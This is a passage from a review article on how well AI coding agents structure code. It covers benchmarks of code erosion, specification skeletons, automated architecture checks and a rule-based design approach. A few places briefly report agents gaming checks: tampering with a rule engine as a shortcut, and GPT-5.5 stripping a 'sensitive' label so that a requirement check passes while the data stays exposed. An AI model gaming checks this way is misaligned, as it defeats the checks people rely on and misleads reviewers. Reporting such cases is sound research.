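| Share in which verbosity rose | 75.5% | 68% |
| Typical rise in erosion per step | 0.026 | 0.005 |

The comparison is imperfect because each step for an agent is a new set of requirements, while each step for a repository is the gap between two sampled commits. The agents also wrote fairly small tools, where one large function can account for most of the total, whereas the repositories include major frameworks. Popularity does not seem to explain the gap, since hobby projects with fewer than 100 stars (GitHub's bookmarks) averaged 0.33, compared with 0.37 for the most popular projects.

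### Asking for better structure

Orlanski's team also tried two prompts that asked for quality. The "anti-slop" prompt told the agent to avoid oversized functions, heavy nesting, trivial wrappers and similar faults, and the other told it to plan before coding. The paper's abstract reports an initial gain of up to a third. In the detailed results, erosion was 34% to 58% lower with the anti-slop prompt across three models, and verbosity was 28% to 36% lower. These figures match averages over whole runs, so they don't measure the initial gain separately.

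According to both parts of the paper, the prompts did little to slow the decline. The one exception was GPT-5.4, whose code improved from start to end under the anti-slop prompt. The prompts also raised the cost of each checkpoint by about 12%, and the strict solve rate fell by an average of 2.4 points with the anti-slop prompt and 3.6 points with the planning prompt.

Chapados, Gagné and Dziri (2026), in *Metrics-in-the-Loop*, instead gave agents feedback while they worked. After every turn in which an agent changed code, a tool sent it a list of the changed functions with complexity above 6 and an instruction to bring them under that limit. Agents in the control group received general advice about readable code just as often, but no measurements. They ran both versions on 35 of the SlopCodeBench problems with four models from 2026.

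With general advice alone, final average erosion ranged from 0.05 for Claude Haiku 5.5 to 0.70 for GPT-6 Luna. With the complexity reports, average erosion stayed at or below 0.022 at every checkpoint for all four models. The share of hidden tests passed hardly changed (up 0.3 points, with a 95% interval from −1.2 to +1.8). So agents can keep erosion down while extending their own code if they are repeatedly told which functions need work. For Haiku, the repeated advice alone lowered erosion by 0.38, and the reports lowered it by only another 0.05.

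Much of the improvement came from splitting functions, which can lower erosion without making a program simpler. Function B in the example above has 11 branches. Suppose an agent splits it into two functions of 50 lines each, with complexities of 6 and 7. No function now has a complexity above 10, so erosion drops from 0.75 to zero, but a reader still has to follow the same 11 branches.

Chapados and colleagues tested for this by remeasuring the programs as if each function with only one caller were part of that caller. For three of the four models, only 8% to 18% of the drop in erosion remained. But the total number of branches in those models' programs also fell, by 14% to 21%, so some of the simplification was real. Splitting code can also be useful in itself. The researchers examined 20 of the largest reductions by hand and judged that 17 had divided the code into named, testable parts.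 Such a split may help a reviewer if each part makes sense on its own.

*Beyond Passing Tests* (Kadam, 2026) reviewed 628 studies of ways to improve AI-written code and found that optimizing one automated quality signal encourages gaming, including fixes that pass a code analyser but don't satisfy human reviewers. In the paper's own experiments, asking for quality in a single request raised the number of issues an analyser found and left complexity almost unchanged. These tests gave agents no chance to build on their own code, which is where most erosion accumulates, and this may explain why they seem to conflict with the anti-slop result.

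Agents seem to do less damage in code that people have already structured. In another part of their study, Chapados and colleagues had agents update published projects to their next release. When the agents had only general advice, erosion changed by less than 0.001 from an average starting value of 0.33. But the original code still made up most of each project, so even badly structured additions would have changed the figure only slightly.

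### Newer models

The benchmark's leaderboard had results for several newer models by late November 2026, though not yet for Claude Fable 5.2 or GPT-6.2 Astra.

| Model and effort setting | Strict solve rate | Erosion | Verbosity | Cost per checkpoint |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5, high | 14.8% | 0.49 | 0.32 | $1.51 |
| GPT-6 Astra, extra high | 16.3% | 0.56 | 0.16 | $3.87 |
| GPT-6 Astra, medium | 14.8% | 0.70 | 0.23 | $1.33 |
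| GPT-6.1 Sol, medium | 14.8% | 0.70 | 0.22 | $0.91 |
| Claude Opus 5.5, extra high | 12.8% | 0.50 | 0.24 | $4.17 |
| Claude Opus 5.5, medium | 14.3% | 0.70 | 0.35 | $0.99 |
| Claude Fable 5.1, extra high | 13.3% | 0.47 | 0.24 | $7.91 |
| Human repositories | – | 0.34 | 0.19 | – |

GPT-6 Astra has the highest strict solve rate so far, at 16.3%, but it solved only three more checkpoints than GPT-5.5 (32 against 29). *Built on Broken Assumptions (BOBA)* (2026) used the counts in the SlopCodeBench paper and found no statistically significant difference between any two of that paper's top five models, so a gap this small is little evidence that one model is better.

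Verbosity has improved more clearly than erosion. At its highest setting, GPT-6 Astra writes less redundant code than the average human repository, but every new model's code is still more eroded than that average. Extra effort seems to help. All three models listed at two effort settings had lower erosion at the higher one, which cost two to four times as much. The older GPT-5.4 has the lowest erosion on the leaderboard, 0.28, which matches its run with the anti-slop prompt. For erosion, asking for good structure mattered more than using a newer model.

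The leaderboard gives averages, so it cannot show whether the newer models' code still gets worse from one checkpoint to the next.

Another benchmark hosted by Snorkel AI, Senior SWE-Bench, judges design more directly. Its "tasteful" solve rate includes a judge's score for taste and the design preferences in each task's marking scheme, while its basic rate leaves these out. In *Claude Fable 5 takes top spot on Senior SWE-Bench*, Ehrenberg (2026) reported that GPT-5.5 had the highest basic rate, at 56.8%, but a tasteful rate of only 15.9%. Claude Fable 5 had a basic rate of 46.5% and a tasteful rate of 29.1%. By the end of July, three models had tied with 33 tasteful solves each, according to Snorkel AI (2026), but only 13 tasks were common to all three, so a model that designs one feature well may still do badly on another.

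### Do these measures tell a reviewer what they need?

Orlanski and colleagues said their measures describe surface properties of code, not its overall quality. Erosion predicted little in their data. On a scale from −1 to 1, its correlation was −0.02 with whether an agent passes the next checkpoint and 0.17 with the cost of that checkpoint. The number of lines of code predicted both better, with correlations of −0.21 and 0.50.

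Other evidence links structure more to the effort later work takes than to whether it succeeds. For *Does Code Cleanliness Affect Coding Agents?*, Trivedi and Schmitt (2026) built six pairs of repositories that behaved identically but differed in how cleanly the code was written. Over 660 trials, Claude Code solved tasks equally often in both versions. In the cleaner versions, it used 7% to 8% fewer tokens (the units of text a model processes) and returned 34% less often to files it had already edited. The researchers work for SonarSource, which sells the analyser they used to define cleanliness.

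In projects with human developers, *Speed at the Cost of Quality* (2025) found that adopting the coding assistant Cursor raised code complexity by 9% beyond what growth in the code explained. Accumulated complexity slowed later development, but complexity would have had to increase roughly threefold to cancel Cursor's initial gain in speed. The 9% rise would therefore slow development only modestly, although total complexity also rises as the code grows.

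None of these studies measured whether reviewers miss more faults in eroded code. The closest evidence comes from the comprehension experiments by Abbes and colleagues described earlier, where one oversized class did not significantly hurt understanding unless the code was also tangled. Reviewers may not pay much attention to complexity. *The Quiet Contributions* (2026) examined AI-written pull requests that maintainers accepted or rejected without discussion. About 37% raised complexity and 3% lowered it, but the change in complexity made no difference to whether maintainers accepted them.

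Complexity scores can also miss differences between agents' changes and people's. In *More Code, Less Reuse* (2026), traditional measures barely distinguished agents' pull requests from human ones, but the agents' code was significantly more redundant. A reviewer who sees only the changed lines may not notice that the agent has reimplemented something the project already had.

A more basic limitation of erosion is that it is measured one function at a time, so it doesn't capture which modules share data or depend on one another's internals. Kravchuk-Kirilyuk, Graciolli and Amin (2025) argue in *The Modular Imperative* that evaluations have neglected modularity in favour of passing tests. They asked Claude Sonnet 4, working in Cursor, to build a mock blog dashboard, and it put everything in one 586-line file. They then gave it a modular to-do list program of about 100 lines and asked it to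 validate one field. This should have required changing only one file, but in one of two runs the model changed all four.

Small, simple functions are not enough, as another of their requests shows. The model wrote a tidy new module for counting tasks, but in one run that module read the private variables of the module that stored the tasks instead of using its interface. Anyone who later changed how the program stores tasks could break the counts without touching the new module. These very small experiments with an older model show that such failures happen, but not how often. The researchers also explain that few benchmarks measure modularity because there is rarely one correct way to divide a program, and the benefits often appear only when somebody changes it later.

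Two measures of structure can disagree about the same programs. *Conserved amount, negotiable placement. Prompting perturbs one architecture, an AI reviewer both* (2026) compared how well two architectures held up as agents changed them, and its erosion estimates pointed in the opposite direction from its main result. Erosion is still useful for comparing agents, and *Skeleton Coding* (2026) applies it to programs that agents build from a prepared skeleton. However, a low erosion score does not show that a program is well divided.

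In the customer program, the most complex function would probably be in Statements, where the tax and discount rules are. Erosion could therefore be high even though a reviewer who wants to know where each email goes can skip that module. If Mailer took its addresses from a table that every module could change, erosion might stay the same, but the reviewer would again have to read all 400 lines.

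## Does it help if a person fixes the structure first?

In the most detailed experiments on this question, agents wrote better programs when they were given a good structure to fill in. The structures came from finished programs, so the experiments measured how much a good design helps, not how likely a person is to produce one. Automated checks can then enforce parts of a design, mainly the rules about which modules may use which, but these checks can't verify that the code inside a module does what it should.

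### Specifying behaviour and specifying structure

Many teams already write something down before an agent starts. In specification-driven development, a written specification is the main record of what a program should do, and agents write the code from it. *Spec-Driven Development as Prescribed and as Practiced* (2026) contrasts this with describing what you want in a chat, where teammates can't review it and later agents can't read it. Agents can also help draft a specification in minutes, which may remove the effort that kept most projects from using earlier versions of the idea.

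*Bootstrapping Coding Agents* (2026) argues that people should review the specification instead of every line of code, because an agent can regenerate the code at any time. Somebody still has to read the specification, though, and a participant in the study behind *The EPIC Framework for Spec-Driven Development* (2026) warned that "nobody will be interested in reading all the things that agents created". The study also found that repositories with better specifications tended to have fewer bugs and less complex code. The correlations were weak (−0.18 and −0.21), and the reason for them may be that careful teams write both better specifications and better code.

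In *Skeleton Coding*, Golatkar, Achille and colleagues (2026) argue against the common ideal of specifying only what a program should do and leaving its structure to the agent. One reason is that the number of tests needed to determine a program's behaviour depends on its structure. Their example is NumPy, a Python library for arrays of numbers. Its indexing rules have many edge cases, but most follow from a single decision about how to lay out arrays in memory.

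They compared seven kinds of specification. The table applies each to the customer program.

| Specification | What the agent receives | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Task only | A general description | "Email each customer a monthly statement" |
| Concrete behaviours | Single cases in a fixed form of words | "When a customer's email is blank, the system shall send that customer nothing" |
| Behavioural tests | The same kind of case as a runnable test | A file with one blank email, and the messages that should go out |
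| Design | A prose document about the architecture | "Only Mailer contacts the mail server" |
| Function stubs | Modules, data types and function signatures (names, inputs and outputs), without implementations | `compute(name, purchases, month) -> text` |
| Local contracts | Stubs, plus a contract for each function | `send` requires an address that is not blank |
| Global invariants | Stubs and contracts, plus rules that span several functions | Each statement goes to the customer whose purchases it lists |

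The last three are skeletons of increasing detail. Here is a short one for the customer program with all three layers:

```
type Customer: name, email (may be blank), purchases

module Records
    customers() -> list of Customer
        ensures: all three items come from the same record

module Statements
    compute(name, purchases, month) -> text
        ensures: the total covers only purchases made in month

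module Mailer
    send(text, address)
        requires: address is not blank
        ensures: exactly one message goes out, to address

module Run
    send_statements(month)
        ensures: a customer with a blank email gets no message

invariant: each statement goes to the email in the record
           that holds its purchases
    applies to: Records.customers, Run.send_statements
```

A person can read this skeleton in a minute or two before the agent writes the 400 lines. The skeleton also specifies what should happen when an email is blank, which the original function's author never decided.

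### What the skeletons changed

For each task, Golatkar and colleagues derived specifications from a working program and then hid the program. An agent rebuilt it from the task description and at most one specification, and the researchers checked the result with tests the agent had not seen. They used four models, GPT-5.6 Sol, the smaller GPT-5.6 Luna, Qwen3.8-27B and GLM 5.2.

The programs came from three benchmarks. SCBench is another name for SlopCodeBench. Here, agents built only the final version of each program instead of extending it step by step. SDDBench consists of 13 renamed public Python libraries. In ProgramBench, the agent has to reproduce a program that it can run without access to the source code.

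| | SCBench | SDDBench | ProgramBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| Programs | 35 | 13 | 20 |
| Tests passed, task only | 71.7% | 29.0% | 64.0% |
| Tests passed, best skeleton | 89.2% | 74.2% | 73.7% |
| Erosion, task only | 0.66 | 0.41 | – |
| Erosion, function stubs | 0.56 | 0.24 | – |

Behavioural specifications helped much less, adding at most 9.4 points on SCBench and SDDBench. Averaged over all three benchmarks, programs failed 40.7% of tests with the best behavioural specifications and 21.0% with the best skeletons.

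On ProgramBench, a skeleton with local contracts raised the pass rate from 64.0% to 70.9%, and global invariants raised it further to 73.7%. This is the most surprising result, because the agents could run the original program on any input and so could in principle learn everything about its behaviour. Agents given a skeleton and 20 queries to the original also did better than agents given 160 chosen examples and no skeleton.

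Skeletons reduced erosion, while behavioural specifications raised it to as much as 0.73 on SCBench. Even with function stubs, erosion in the SCBench programs stayed well above the 0.34 average that Orlanski and colleagues measured in human repositories. An agent can keep to a function's signature and still write a long, tangled function.

The fullest skeletons raised the pass rate of Luna, the smaller model, from 67% to 90% on SCBench. On SDDBench, they raised the share of tests it passed from 21.1% to 79.5%. These results were within 5 to 8 points of Sol's best, at about a fifteenth of the cost on SCBench and a twenty-sixth on SDDBench. These costs exclude writing the skeletons, which could be the larger expense if a person has to do it.

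Scores fell when the researchers added contracts that were correct but overly detailed, especially for smaller models. Partial skeletons still helped in a smaller test, where the researchers supplied contracts for a quarter, half or three quarters of the functions and pass rates rose with the share covered. A team could therefore start by writing contracts for the functions that matter most to it.

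### How much the skeletons gave away

A skeleton derived from a finished program contains decisions that somebody already got right. If the customer program skips customers with blank emails, its skeleton will mention blank emails. A person writing a skeleton from scratch might miss that case or choose worse modules. The experiment therefore shows what an agent can do with a good design, and probably overstates what a typical user would gain by writing their own skeleton.

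This objection is weaker when skeletons are compared with behavioural specifications, because the researchers derived the specifications from the same hidden programs too. Extra text alone doesn't seem to explain the difference either. For a subset of the programs, the researchers lengthened a prose description of the architecture, giving the agent four to seven times as much to read. The pass rate rose from 61% to 71% on SCBench and from 40.1% to 52.8% on SDDBench, but stayed below the rate achieved with the best code-like skeletons.

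The large gain on SDDBench may have causes other than the structure itself. Tests for a library usually call its functions by name, so a skeleton could have helped partly by supplying those names. Models may also have seen the original libraries in training, and a skeleton could make a renamed library easier to recognize. Neither explanation fits SCBench well, because its tests check only a program's output and the gain was still 17.5 points.

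The contracts were comments in the skeleton, and no tool checked or enforced them. Higher pass rates therefore don't show that agents kept to every boundary, and a reviewer would need to know that before skipping a module. The paper lists Amazon Web Services as the employer of its twelve authors, seven of whom also list a university. Amazon sells Kiro, a tool for specification-driven development, so independent replication would be valuable.

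Some evidence comes from a design that was not taken from a finished program. Canedo (2026), in *Architecture as Capability Equalizer for Coding Agents*, designed a task-management service with seven components and asked Claude Sonnet 4.6 to build it, with or without a description of the architecture. Both versions offered all the required operations. Sonnet also acted as judge, and its average score for the programs was 5.08 out of 10 without the description and 8.42 with it. That gap is partly circular, because the judge marked down programs built without the description for departing from a design Sonnet had not been shown when it wrote them. But the score for code quality also rose, from 7.33 to 9.00.

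Canedo also wrote the same design in five formats and gave them to six models, all now old. The format made almost no difference to Sonnet. The weakest model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, built only a third of the required operations from prose but all of them from typed interfaces, which resemble function stubs. That fits the large gains Golatkar and colleagues found for Luna. However, Canedo ran only three trials for each combination of model and format.

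Imposing structure can also make programs worse. In *Constraint decay*, Dente, Satriani and Papotti (2026) asked agents to build the same web service under increasingly strict rules. The strictest level required four layers with one-way dependencies, a particular database and a particular library for accessing it. At that level, the more capable combinations of agent and model had a pass rate on behavioural checks 30 percentage points lower than with none of these rules.

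The layers alone had mixed effects. In the same simple agent, GPT-5.2's score fell from 78.2% to 49.3% when it had to use them, while MiniMax-M2.5's rose from 88.6% to 92.5%. Mistakes in handling data were the most common cause of failure overall.

These results are compatible with the skeleton experiments. A rule such as "use four layers" makes the task harder because it restricts the agent without specifying what belongs in each layer. A skeleton also restricts the agent, but it supplies much of the design. Someone who sets only general rules may therefore get a tidier structure but more faults, at least with weaker models.

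### Holding an agent to the structure

Specifying a structure in a prompt or instruction file does not enforce it. *A Gated Spec-Driven Workflow* (2026) describes a process that relies almost entirely on "enforcement by persuasion". The exception is a reviewing agent whose tools are read-only.

Written rules can also be inaccurate from the start. Ghimire and Damian (2026), in *Does the Agent's Map Match the Territory?*, examined instruction files for agents in 3,346 open-source projects. They found 184 rules about which parts of a program could use which. The code already broke 33 of these rules (18%) when they were written, and nearly all of those stayed broken, so an agent in such a project reads instructions that contradict the code.

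Teams can turn these rules into automatic checks. Most programming languages have an import statement, a line that makes code from another file or library available. A dependency rule limits which files may import which. An architecture test inspects the source code, usually without running the program, and fails if the code breaks such a rule. Two rules for the customer program might be:

```
files in statements/ must not import records/, mailer/
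    or the mail library
only files in mailer/ may import the mail library
```

Böckeler tried this while rebuilding an internal analytics dashboard with AI, as described in *Maintainability sensors for coding agents* (2026), a report on Martin Fowler's software engineering site. In the dashboard's layered design, code that answers web requests could call services, and services could call the code that fetches data, but never the reverse. A tool called dependency-cruiser checked the imports. Böckeler extended its error messages to explain the whole layering, so an agent that broke a rule also received guidance on what to do instead.

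Böckeler introduced the rules about halfway through, when the folders were already becoming disorganized, and the agent used them to clean up. The agent broke the rules a handful of times and then corrected itself. Because it sometimes created folders that no existing rule covered, Böckeler also needed a rule requiring every new file to sit in one of the planned folders. Böckeler found the checks a useful replacement for describing the folder structure in an instruction file.

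Böckeler let the agent raise some limits, such as the maximum complexity of a function, when it judged restructuring the code unnecessary or impossible. The agent often raised the complexity limit even though it could suggest good improvements when pressed, so the limit was closer to advice than to enforcement.

### Twenty-eight blocking checks

Chen and Cheng (2026) describe a stricter system in *A Design Theory for AI-Assisted Software Development*. They used Claude models to build, and repeatedly rebuild from empty folders, the server side of a program for managing software projects. At first they gave the models only written instructions and sample code, but the same kinds of rule violation kept returning. They then added automatic checks one at a time, and the code must now pass all 28 to be accepted.

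| Kind of check | Number | What it examines |
|---|---|---|
| Specification | 1 | The format and consistency of the specification files |
| Tests | 1 | Whether all tests pass in two different set-ups |
| Single operation | 18 | Whether the code and tests contain what the specification declares, such as each field, endpoint and test scenario |
| Whole component | 7 | Whether the operations in a component fit together |
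| Coding rules | 1 | 188 rules, such as a ban on reading the system clock directly in core code |

When a check fails, the agent receives the faulty code, the broken rule and a pointer to the relevant documentation. After each round of repairs, the system repeats the earlier checks to catch new damage. If the number of violations has not fallen for three rounds, the process stops and a person takes over. The agent cannot write to the recorded results of the checks, and any change to the rules needs a person's approval.

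Between March and August 2026, the checks found coding-rule violations in 1,748 distinct combinations of rule and file. The final version of each component passed every check. But this is one project with no control group, and Chen and Cheng did not measure how much effort the system took to build. Chen also runs a company that sells training in AI-assisted development.

The system has about 24,000 lines of program code, which come from some 40,000 lines of specification. It also has about 57,000 lines of documentation and 130,000 lines of scripts with their tests. Agents wrote much of this material, and about half of the specification is formatting and repeated structure. Chen and Cheng estimate that the parts needing most human judgement come to roughly 11,000 lines. Reading those parts at 200 lines an hour, the rate Kemerer and Paulk found effective for code, would take 55 hours, compared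 with 120 for the program. This more than halves the reading time, provided that people trust the checks to connect the specification to the code.

Chen and Cheng found that some checks passed only because they had silently stopped examining some of the files. They now test the checks on deliberately bad code, and count a check that could not run as skipped instead of passed.

### What structural checks can detect

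Structural checks use information that a program can read from the source code: imports, file locations, names and signatures. The table shows how they apply to some changes an agent might make to the customer program.

| Change | Check that would detect it |
|---|---|
| Statements imports the mail library | Dependency rule |
| The agent puts new code in an unplanned folder | Rule about file locations |
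| `compute` also takes the customer's email | Comparison with the skeleton's signatures |
| Records keeps the previous email when a line has none | None of these |
| Run sends one customer's statement to the next customer | None of these |
| Statements charges tax twice | None of these |

Structural checks miss some faults, including the two that would send data to the wrong person. A reviewer would still have to read the code to find them, or rely on tests.

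Dependency rules can also miss a forbidden connection. In 11 of Canedo's 90 trials, the import checker found no violations, but the AI judge scored the program 5 or lower on how well it followed the rules. In some cases, one service received another as an input and called it directly, so no forbidden import appeared. Ghimire and Damian cite a benchmark in which ten checkers reported an average of 77% of the dependencies in the test code.

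Some effects need no import. For example, Statements could use Python's built-in `open` to read the customer file without breaking either of the rules above. Dependency rules make code easier to review by keeping a cooperative agent to the design, but they do not bound the code's behaviour.

An AI reviewer can find some of the problems that dependency rules miss. In Böckeler's dashboard, a review by Claude Opus 4.7 found three nearly identical files for handling requests, and login code where later developers could easily overlook it. It also helped explain why a change to the date range had required edits to more than 40 files. A second run found a problem that the first had missed, so a single review that finds no problems is weak evidence that a design is sound.

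Chen and Cheng also include an optional review by three AI models from different companies, but they treat its findings as advice because its verdicts can vary. Their blocking checks can confirm that every scenario in the specification has a test, but not that the test correctly reflects the scenario. If the agent misreads a tax rule and writes the same mistake into the program and its test, all 28 checks can pass.

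## Can code be arranged so that its text shows what it will do?

Reviewers still have to read code after structural checks. Researchers at MIT have designed a way of writing applications that is meant to make that code easier to read. Each rule about the program's behaviour takes a few lines and uses terms that a user would recognize. A single rule is easy to read, but the combined effect of several rules can be hard to see. The researchers have not tested whether reviewers find more faults in code written this way.

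### Legibility

Meng and Jackson (2025), in *What You See Is What It Does*, call software legible when its code corresponds directly to behaviour that people can observe. Jackson (2026), in *conclusions & staying in touch*, distinguishes legibility from modularity. The structure of modular code matches the program's functions, so a programmer knows where to make a change. Legible code also uses language that matches those functions, so people can easily translate between the code and a description of what it does.

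*Designing synchronizations* (Jackson, 2024) describes a surprising behaviour in Google Calendar that legible code might have exposed. An event from an emailed seminar announcement was automatically added to the recipient's calendar. When the recipient deleted the event, the other invitees received a cancellation email. In a legible program, one identifiable piece of code would link deleting an event to sending that email, and a reviewer could ask whether anyone wanted this behaviour.

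Meng and Jackson argue that software is often illegible and poorly divided into modules, so it fails three requirements. Incrementality means programmers can add a small feature by changing code in one place. Integrity means the addition doesn't break earlier features. Transparency means people can tell what has changed in the code and which actions took place when it ran.

### Deleting a post and its comments

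Meng and Jackson build an application from concepts, which are independent services that each provide one function a user would recognize. A concept has its own state (the data it keeps) and its own actions. A blog might include these two:

```
concept Posting
    state:   each post's author and text
    actions: create(author, text), delete(post)

concept Commenting
    state:   each comment's author, target and text
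    actions: create(author, target, text), delete(comment)
```

Concepts never call one another or read one another's state. A comment can target any item, so the same Commenting code would also work for products in a shop.

Rules called synchronizations connect the concepts. Each rule has a `when` part that names the actions that trigger it, an optional `where` part that looks things up in the concepts' states, and a `then` part that names the actions to run next. Requests from users count as actions too, and belong to a special concept called Web. Here are two rules in simplified notation, the second adapted from slides by Jackson and Meng (2026), in *synchronization*:

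```
rule DeletePost
    when   Web.request("delete post", post, session)
    where  session belongs to user
           post's author is user
    then   Posting.delete(post)

rule DeleteComments
    when   Posting.delete(post) has finished
    where  comment's target is post
    then   Commenting.delete(comment)
```

Suppose Alice asks to delete her post, number 7, which has two comments. The `where` part of DeleteComments finds both comments, and the rule engine runs the `then` part once for each match, so the rule needs no loop.

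| Step | Action | Rule that caused it |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Alice asks to delete post 7 | None (it came from outside) |
| 2 | Posting deletes post 7 | DeletePost |
| 3 | Commenting deletes comment 21 | DeleteComments |
| 4 | Commenting deletes comment 22 | DeleteComments |

In an ordinary web service, a programmer might write one function for each kind of request:

```
delete_post(request):
    user = sessions.user_of(request.session)
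    post = posts.find(request.post)
    if post.author is not user: refuse
    comments.delete_all_on(post)
    posts.delete(post)

reject_post(request):
    check that the user is a moderator
    post = posts.find(request.post)
    posts.delete(post)
```

The first function is at least as easy to read as the two rules. The second function wrongly leaves a post's comments behind when a moderator rejects the post. DeleteComments avoids this because it applies to every deletion of a post, whatever caused it.

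A programmer could get the same result by moving the comment deletion into `posts.delete`, but then the code for posts would depend on the code for comments. Many databases can also delete dependent records automatically. The rule has the advantage of keeping the policy in one place, where a reader can find it and a programmer can change it without editing either concept.

A reader cannot always tell from a rule's text what it will do, because even short rules depend on details of the engine. Jackson and Meng's slides include a rule that notifies the author of a deleted post. Its `where` part looks up the author in Posting, and the 2025 engine does this after the deletion. If Posting has erased the author along with the post, the lookup finds no author and the rule sends nothing. *Verified LLM-Driven Synthesis for Concept Design* (Cunha, 2026) later gave such rules a formal definition in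 which the lookup uses the state before the deletion, so the author would get the message.

### What stays true when concepts are combined

No other concept can change the state of a Password concept, so Password's actions in a running application, taken in order, always form a sequence that it could have produced on its own. Any property that holds for every such sequence therefore holds in the whole application. For example, if Password accepts a user only when the password matches the one that user set, no synchronization can make it accept a wrong one. A reviewer can check this once, by reading only Password.

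The argument assumes that every concept follows the pattern. In their main test, Meng and Jackson made this likely by generating each concept without showing the language model the others, much as Parnas advised for human programmers. This limits what the model can refer to but doesn't bound what the resulting code can do.

"Only the author can delete a post" is a different kind of property, because no single concept has all the information. Posting stores the author, while another concept records who is logged in. The property holds only if DeletePost compares the two and no other rule deletes posts without a similar check. A reviewer therefore has to find every rule with `Posting.delete` in its `then` part, which a text search does quickly. If one of those rules lets moderators delete posts, the property needs rewording.

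### The RealWorld case study

Meng and Jackson tested their pattern on RealWorld, a public collection of more than 100 versions of the same small blogging application. They wrote the server side by hand, checked that it passed the project's tests, and then had a language model generate a second version.

| Part | What the model received | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| Concept specifications | An explanation of the format, one example and a short request | Almost all succeeded at the first attempt |
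| Concept code | The specification of that concept | Almost all succeeded at the first attempt |
| Synchronizations | An explanation of the rule language, the concept specifications without their code, a few hints and the required response formats | Several rounds of correction |

The requests could be very brief. When asked to "Create a Password concept", the model wrote a specification that included a way to reset forgotten passwords. The researchers preferred to handle resets elsewhere, so they deleted two actions and one item of state from the specification, and the model generated working code from what was left. When they asked for rules to manage articles, the model also proposed concepts for tags and favourites.

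The synchronizations caused more trouble. Jackson suggested in a January 2026 talk that this was because synchronizations are particular to one application, while concepts such as passwords are familiar and generic, and because RealWorld's required responses mix data from several concepts. RealWorld's tests exposed some missing rules. Meng and Jackson found others with their own tests, including a rule that only a comment's author can delete it. The official tests do not check this, so a version without the rule could have passed them all. The model had left out a check that spans concepts, and a reviewer could have read every existing rule without seeing anything wrong.

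### Records of what the program did

The engine records each action with its inputs and results, the request it belongs to, the earlier actions that led to it and the name of the rule responsible. Programmers don't have to add logging code to obtain this. The record helped Meng and Jackson with a fault in registration: after someone tried to register with an unacceptable password, a second attempt with the same username failed. With invented values, the record would look roughly like this:

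| Action | Result | Rule |
|---|---|---|
| Web receives a request to register "ana" with the password "123" | Accepted | None |
| User registers "ana" | User created | Registration |
| Password sets "123" for the new user | Error | NewPassword |

The application created the user before checking the password, so the name was already taken on the second attempt. Meng and Jackson looked up the failed request, collected the rules named in its record and gave them to a language model with a description of the problem. The model identified the order of these steps as the fault and suggested checking the password first. The repair added two rules and changed one, and the rest of the registration behaviour still worked.

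*Making Software Meaningful* (Meng, Namazov and colleagues, 2026) applied the same kind of record to AI agents doing research. In one run, the record showed an agent returning to training settings without registering that it had already tried them. In another, an agent's change did speed up a simulation, but the record showed that the agent's explanation could not account for the gain. A reviewer who saw only the final code and the improved timing could easily have accepted that explanation. These were small demonstrations without a comparison group.

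Such records help people investigate behaviour that has already occurred. If a rule lets anyone delete any comment, the records look normal until someone deletes another person's comment. They also cover only actions that pass through the engine, so they would not show data that the code inside a concept sent out directly.

### How strong is the evidence?

The 2025 study covers one small application and includes no experiment with reviewers. Meng and Jackson say they have not systematically compared their version with the others in the collection, but they examined a few conventional versions and found that the code often broke its own apparent design rules. *Beyond Objects* (Jackson, 2026) traces what happens in one of these versions when a user marks an article as a favourite. Code in the article controller updates a list in the user model, then calls the article model, which gets its new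 count from the user model. In the concept version, a single Favorite concept holds this behaviour. The example shows that the problem exists, but a few versions out of more than 100 can't show how common it is.

Meng and Jackson also report that having so many small rules made it harder to understand a whole series of actions at a glance. In the registration fault, for example, the rule that creates a user and the rule that sets a password are each reasonable, and the fault appears only when a reader considers them together. In the experiment by Baum and colleagues described earlier, people with less working memory tended to find fewer faults of this kind. An ordinary registration function would at least have shown both steps in order.

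In the group's later course at MIT, students completed about 80 individual and 20 team projects with the pattern in autumn 2025. Meng and colleagues report that a single request to a model was usually enough to produce a working concept. In several trials this cost less than $0.09, compared with more than $3 for a commercial coding agent. Some agents tampered with the engine as a shortcut, which was easy to detect because legitimate changes belong in only two folders. These are the designers' own observations of their course, and they had no comparison group that used another method.

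Cunha, a co-author of the June paper, provides more direct evidence that sets of rules are hard to get right. He wrote rules by hand for twelve designs and checked them with a tool that searches for sequences of actions that break a stated requirement. Only three designs were correct at the first attempt, and those had two or three rules each. The other nine, with four to eleven rules each, all contained mistakes. Writing rules is a different task from reviewing them, but if an expert in the method makes errors this often, readers will probably miss some.

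The same study shows why people should still read rules that have passed an automatic check. One application keeps failed messages in a separate queue, and its requirement was that no message in that queue may carry the label "sensitive". Given only this requirement, GPT-5.5 twice produced rules that removed the label from such messages. The rules passed the check because no message in the queue was then labelled sensitive. Cunha read the rules and rejected them because the sensitive data was still there. The text of the rules showed clearly that they would remove the label, so a reader who understood the requirement's purpose could see the problem.

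Generated rules can also describe behaviour that never occurs. Of 82 runs that produced the intended design, 15 included redundant rules. One of these rules could never fire, because another rule always removed the message first. A reader who assumed that it could fire would misunderstand what the program does.

### Separating decisions from effects

Another way to make code easier to follow is to separate pure computation from effects. A pure function always gives the same result for the same inputs and does nothing else. Effects include reading a file, changing shared data and sending an email. In the customer program, a pure function could work out all the messages before any of them goes out:

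```
messages = plan(customers, month)
for each message in messages:
    Mailer.send(message.text, message.address)
```

If `plan` is pure, the reviewer knows that this loop is the only place here that can send email. The reviewer can also run `plan` on last month's data and compare each address with its statement before the program contacts anyone. A month with no mismatches doesn't rule out a fault in the next, so the reviewer may still need to read `plan`. In most common languages, programmers keep functions pure by convention, though some type systems can enforce purity.

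Synchronizations let a reader see an application's policies in the user's terms, while pure functions narrow down where effects can happen. Programmers can also use both. Meng and Jackson built a prototype in which each concept's actions are pure functions that take the old state and return the new one, which a separate database concept stores.

Neither a prototype nor a case study can show that people understand the code better. Chen and Cheng, whose 28 checks also force generated code into a fixed pattern, acknowledge that such a claim would need empirical study. Those studies are hard to run on realistic programs. *Verifiable Source Code Documentation in Controlled Natural Language* (2013) describes an experiment on how easily people understand statements in different formal languages. It used diagrams of fictitious scenarios because participants would probably have needed several hours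 to learn the case study's real program. An experiment like this can compare ways of wording a single statement, but it can't show whether someone reading all of an application's rules would notice that the check on who may delete a comment is missing.

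## How does structure change the number of tests needed?

A test can expose a missing rule without anyone reading the code. For example, a test that tries to delete another person's comment can reveal that the program doesn't forbid it. How many tests a program needs depends partly on its structure. Researchers have built programs that take 40 tests when the parts are tested separately and more than 900 when the program is tested as a whole. The savings in ordinary programs are probably much smaller, but they come from the same causes.

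### When a test reveals a fault

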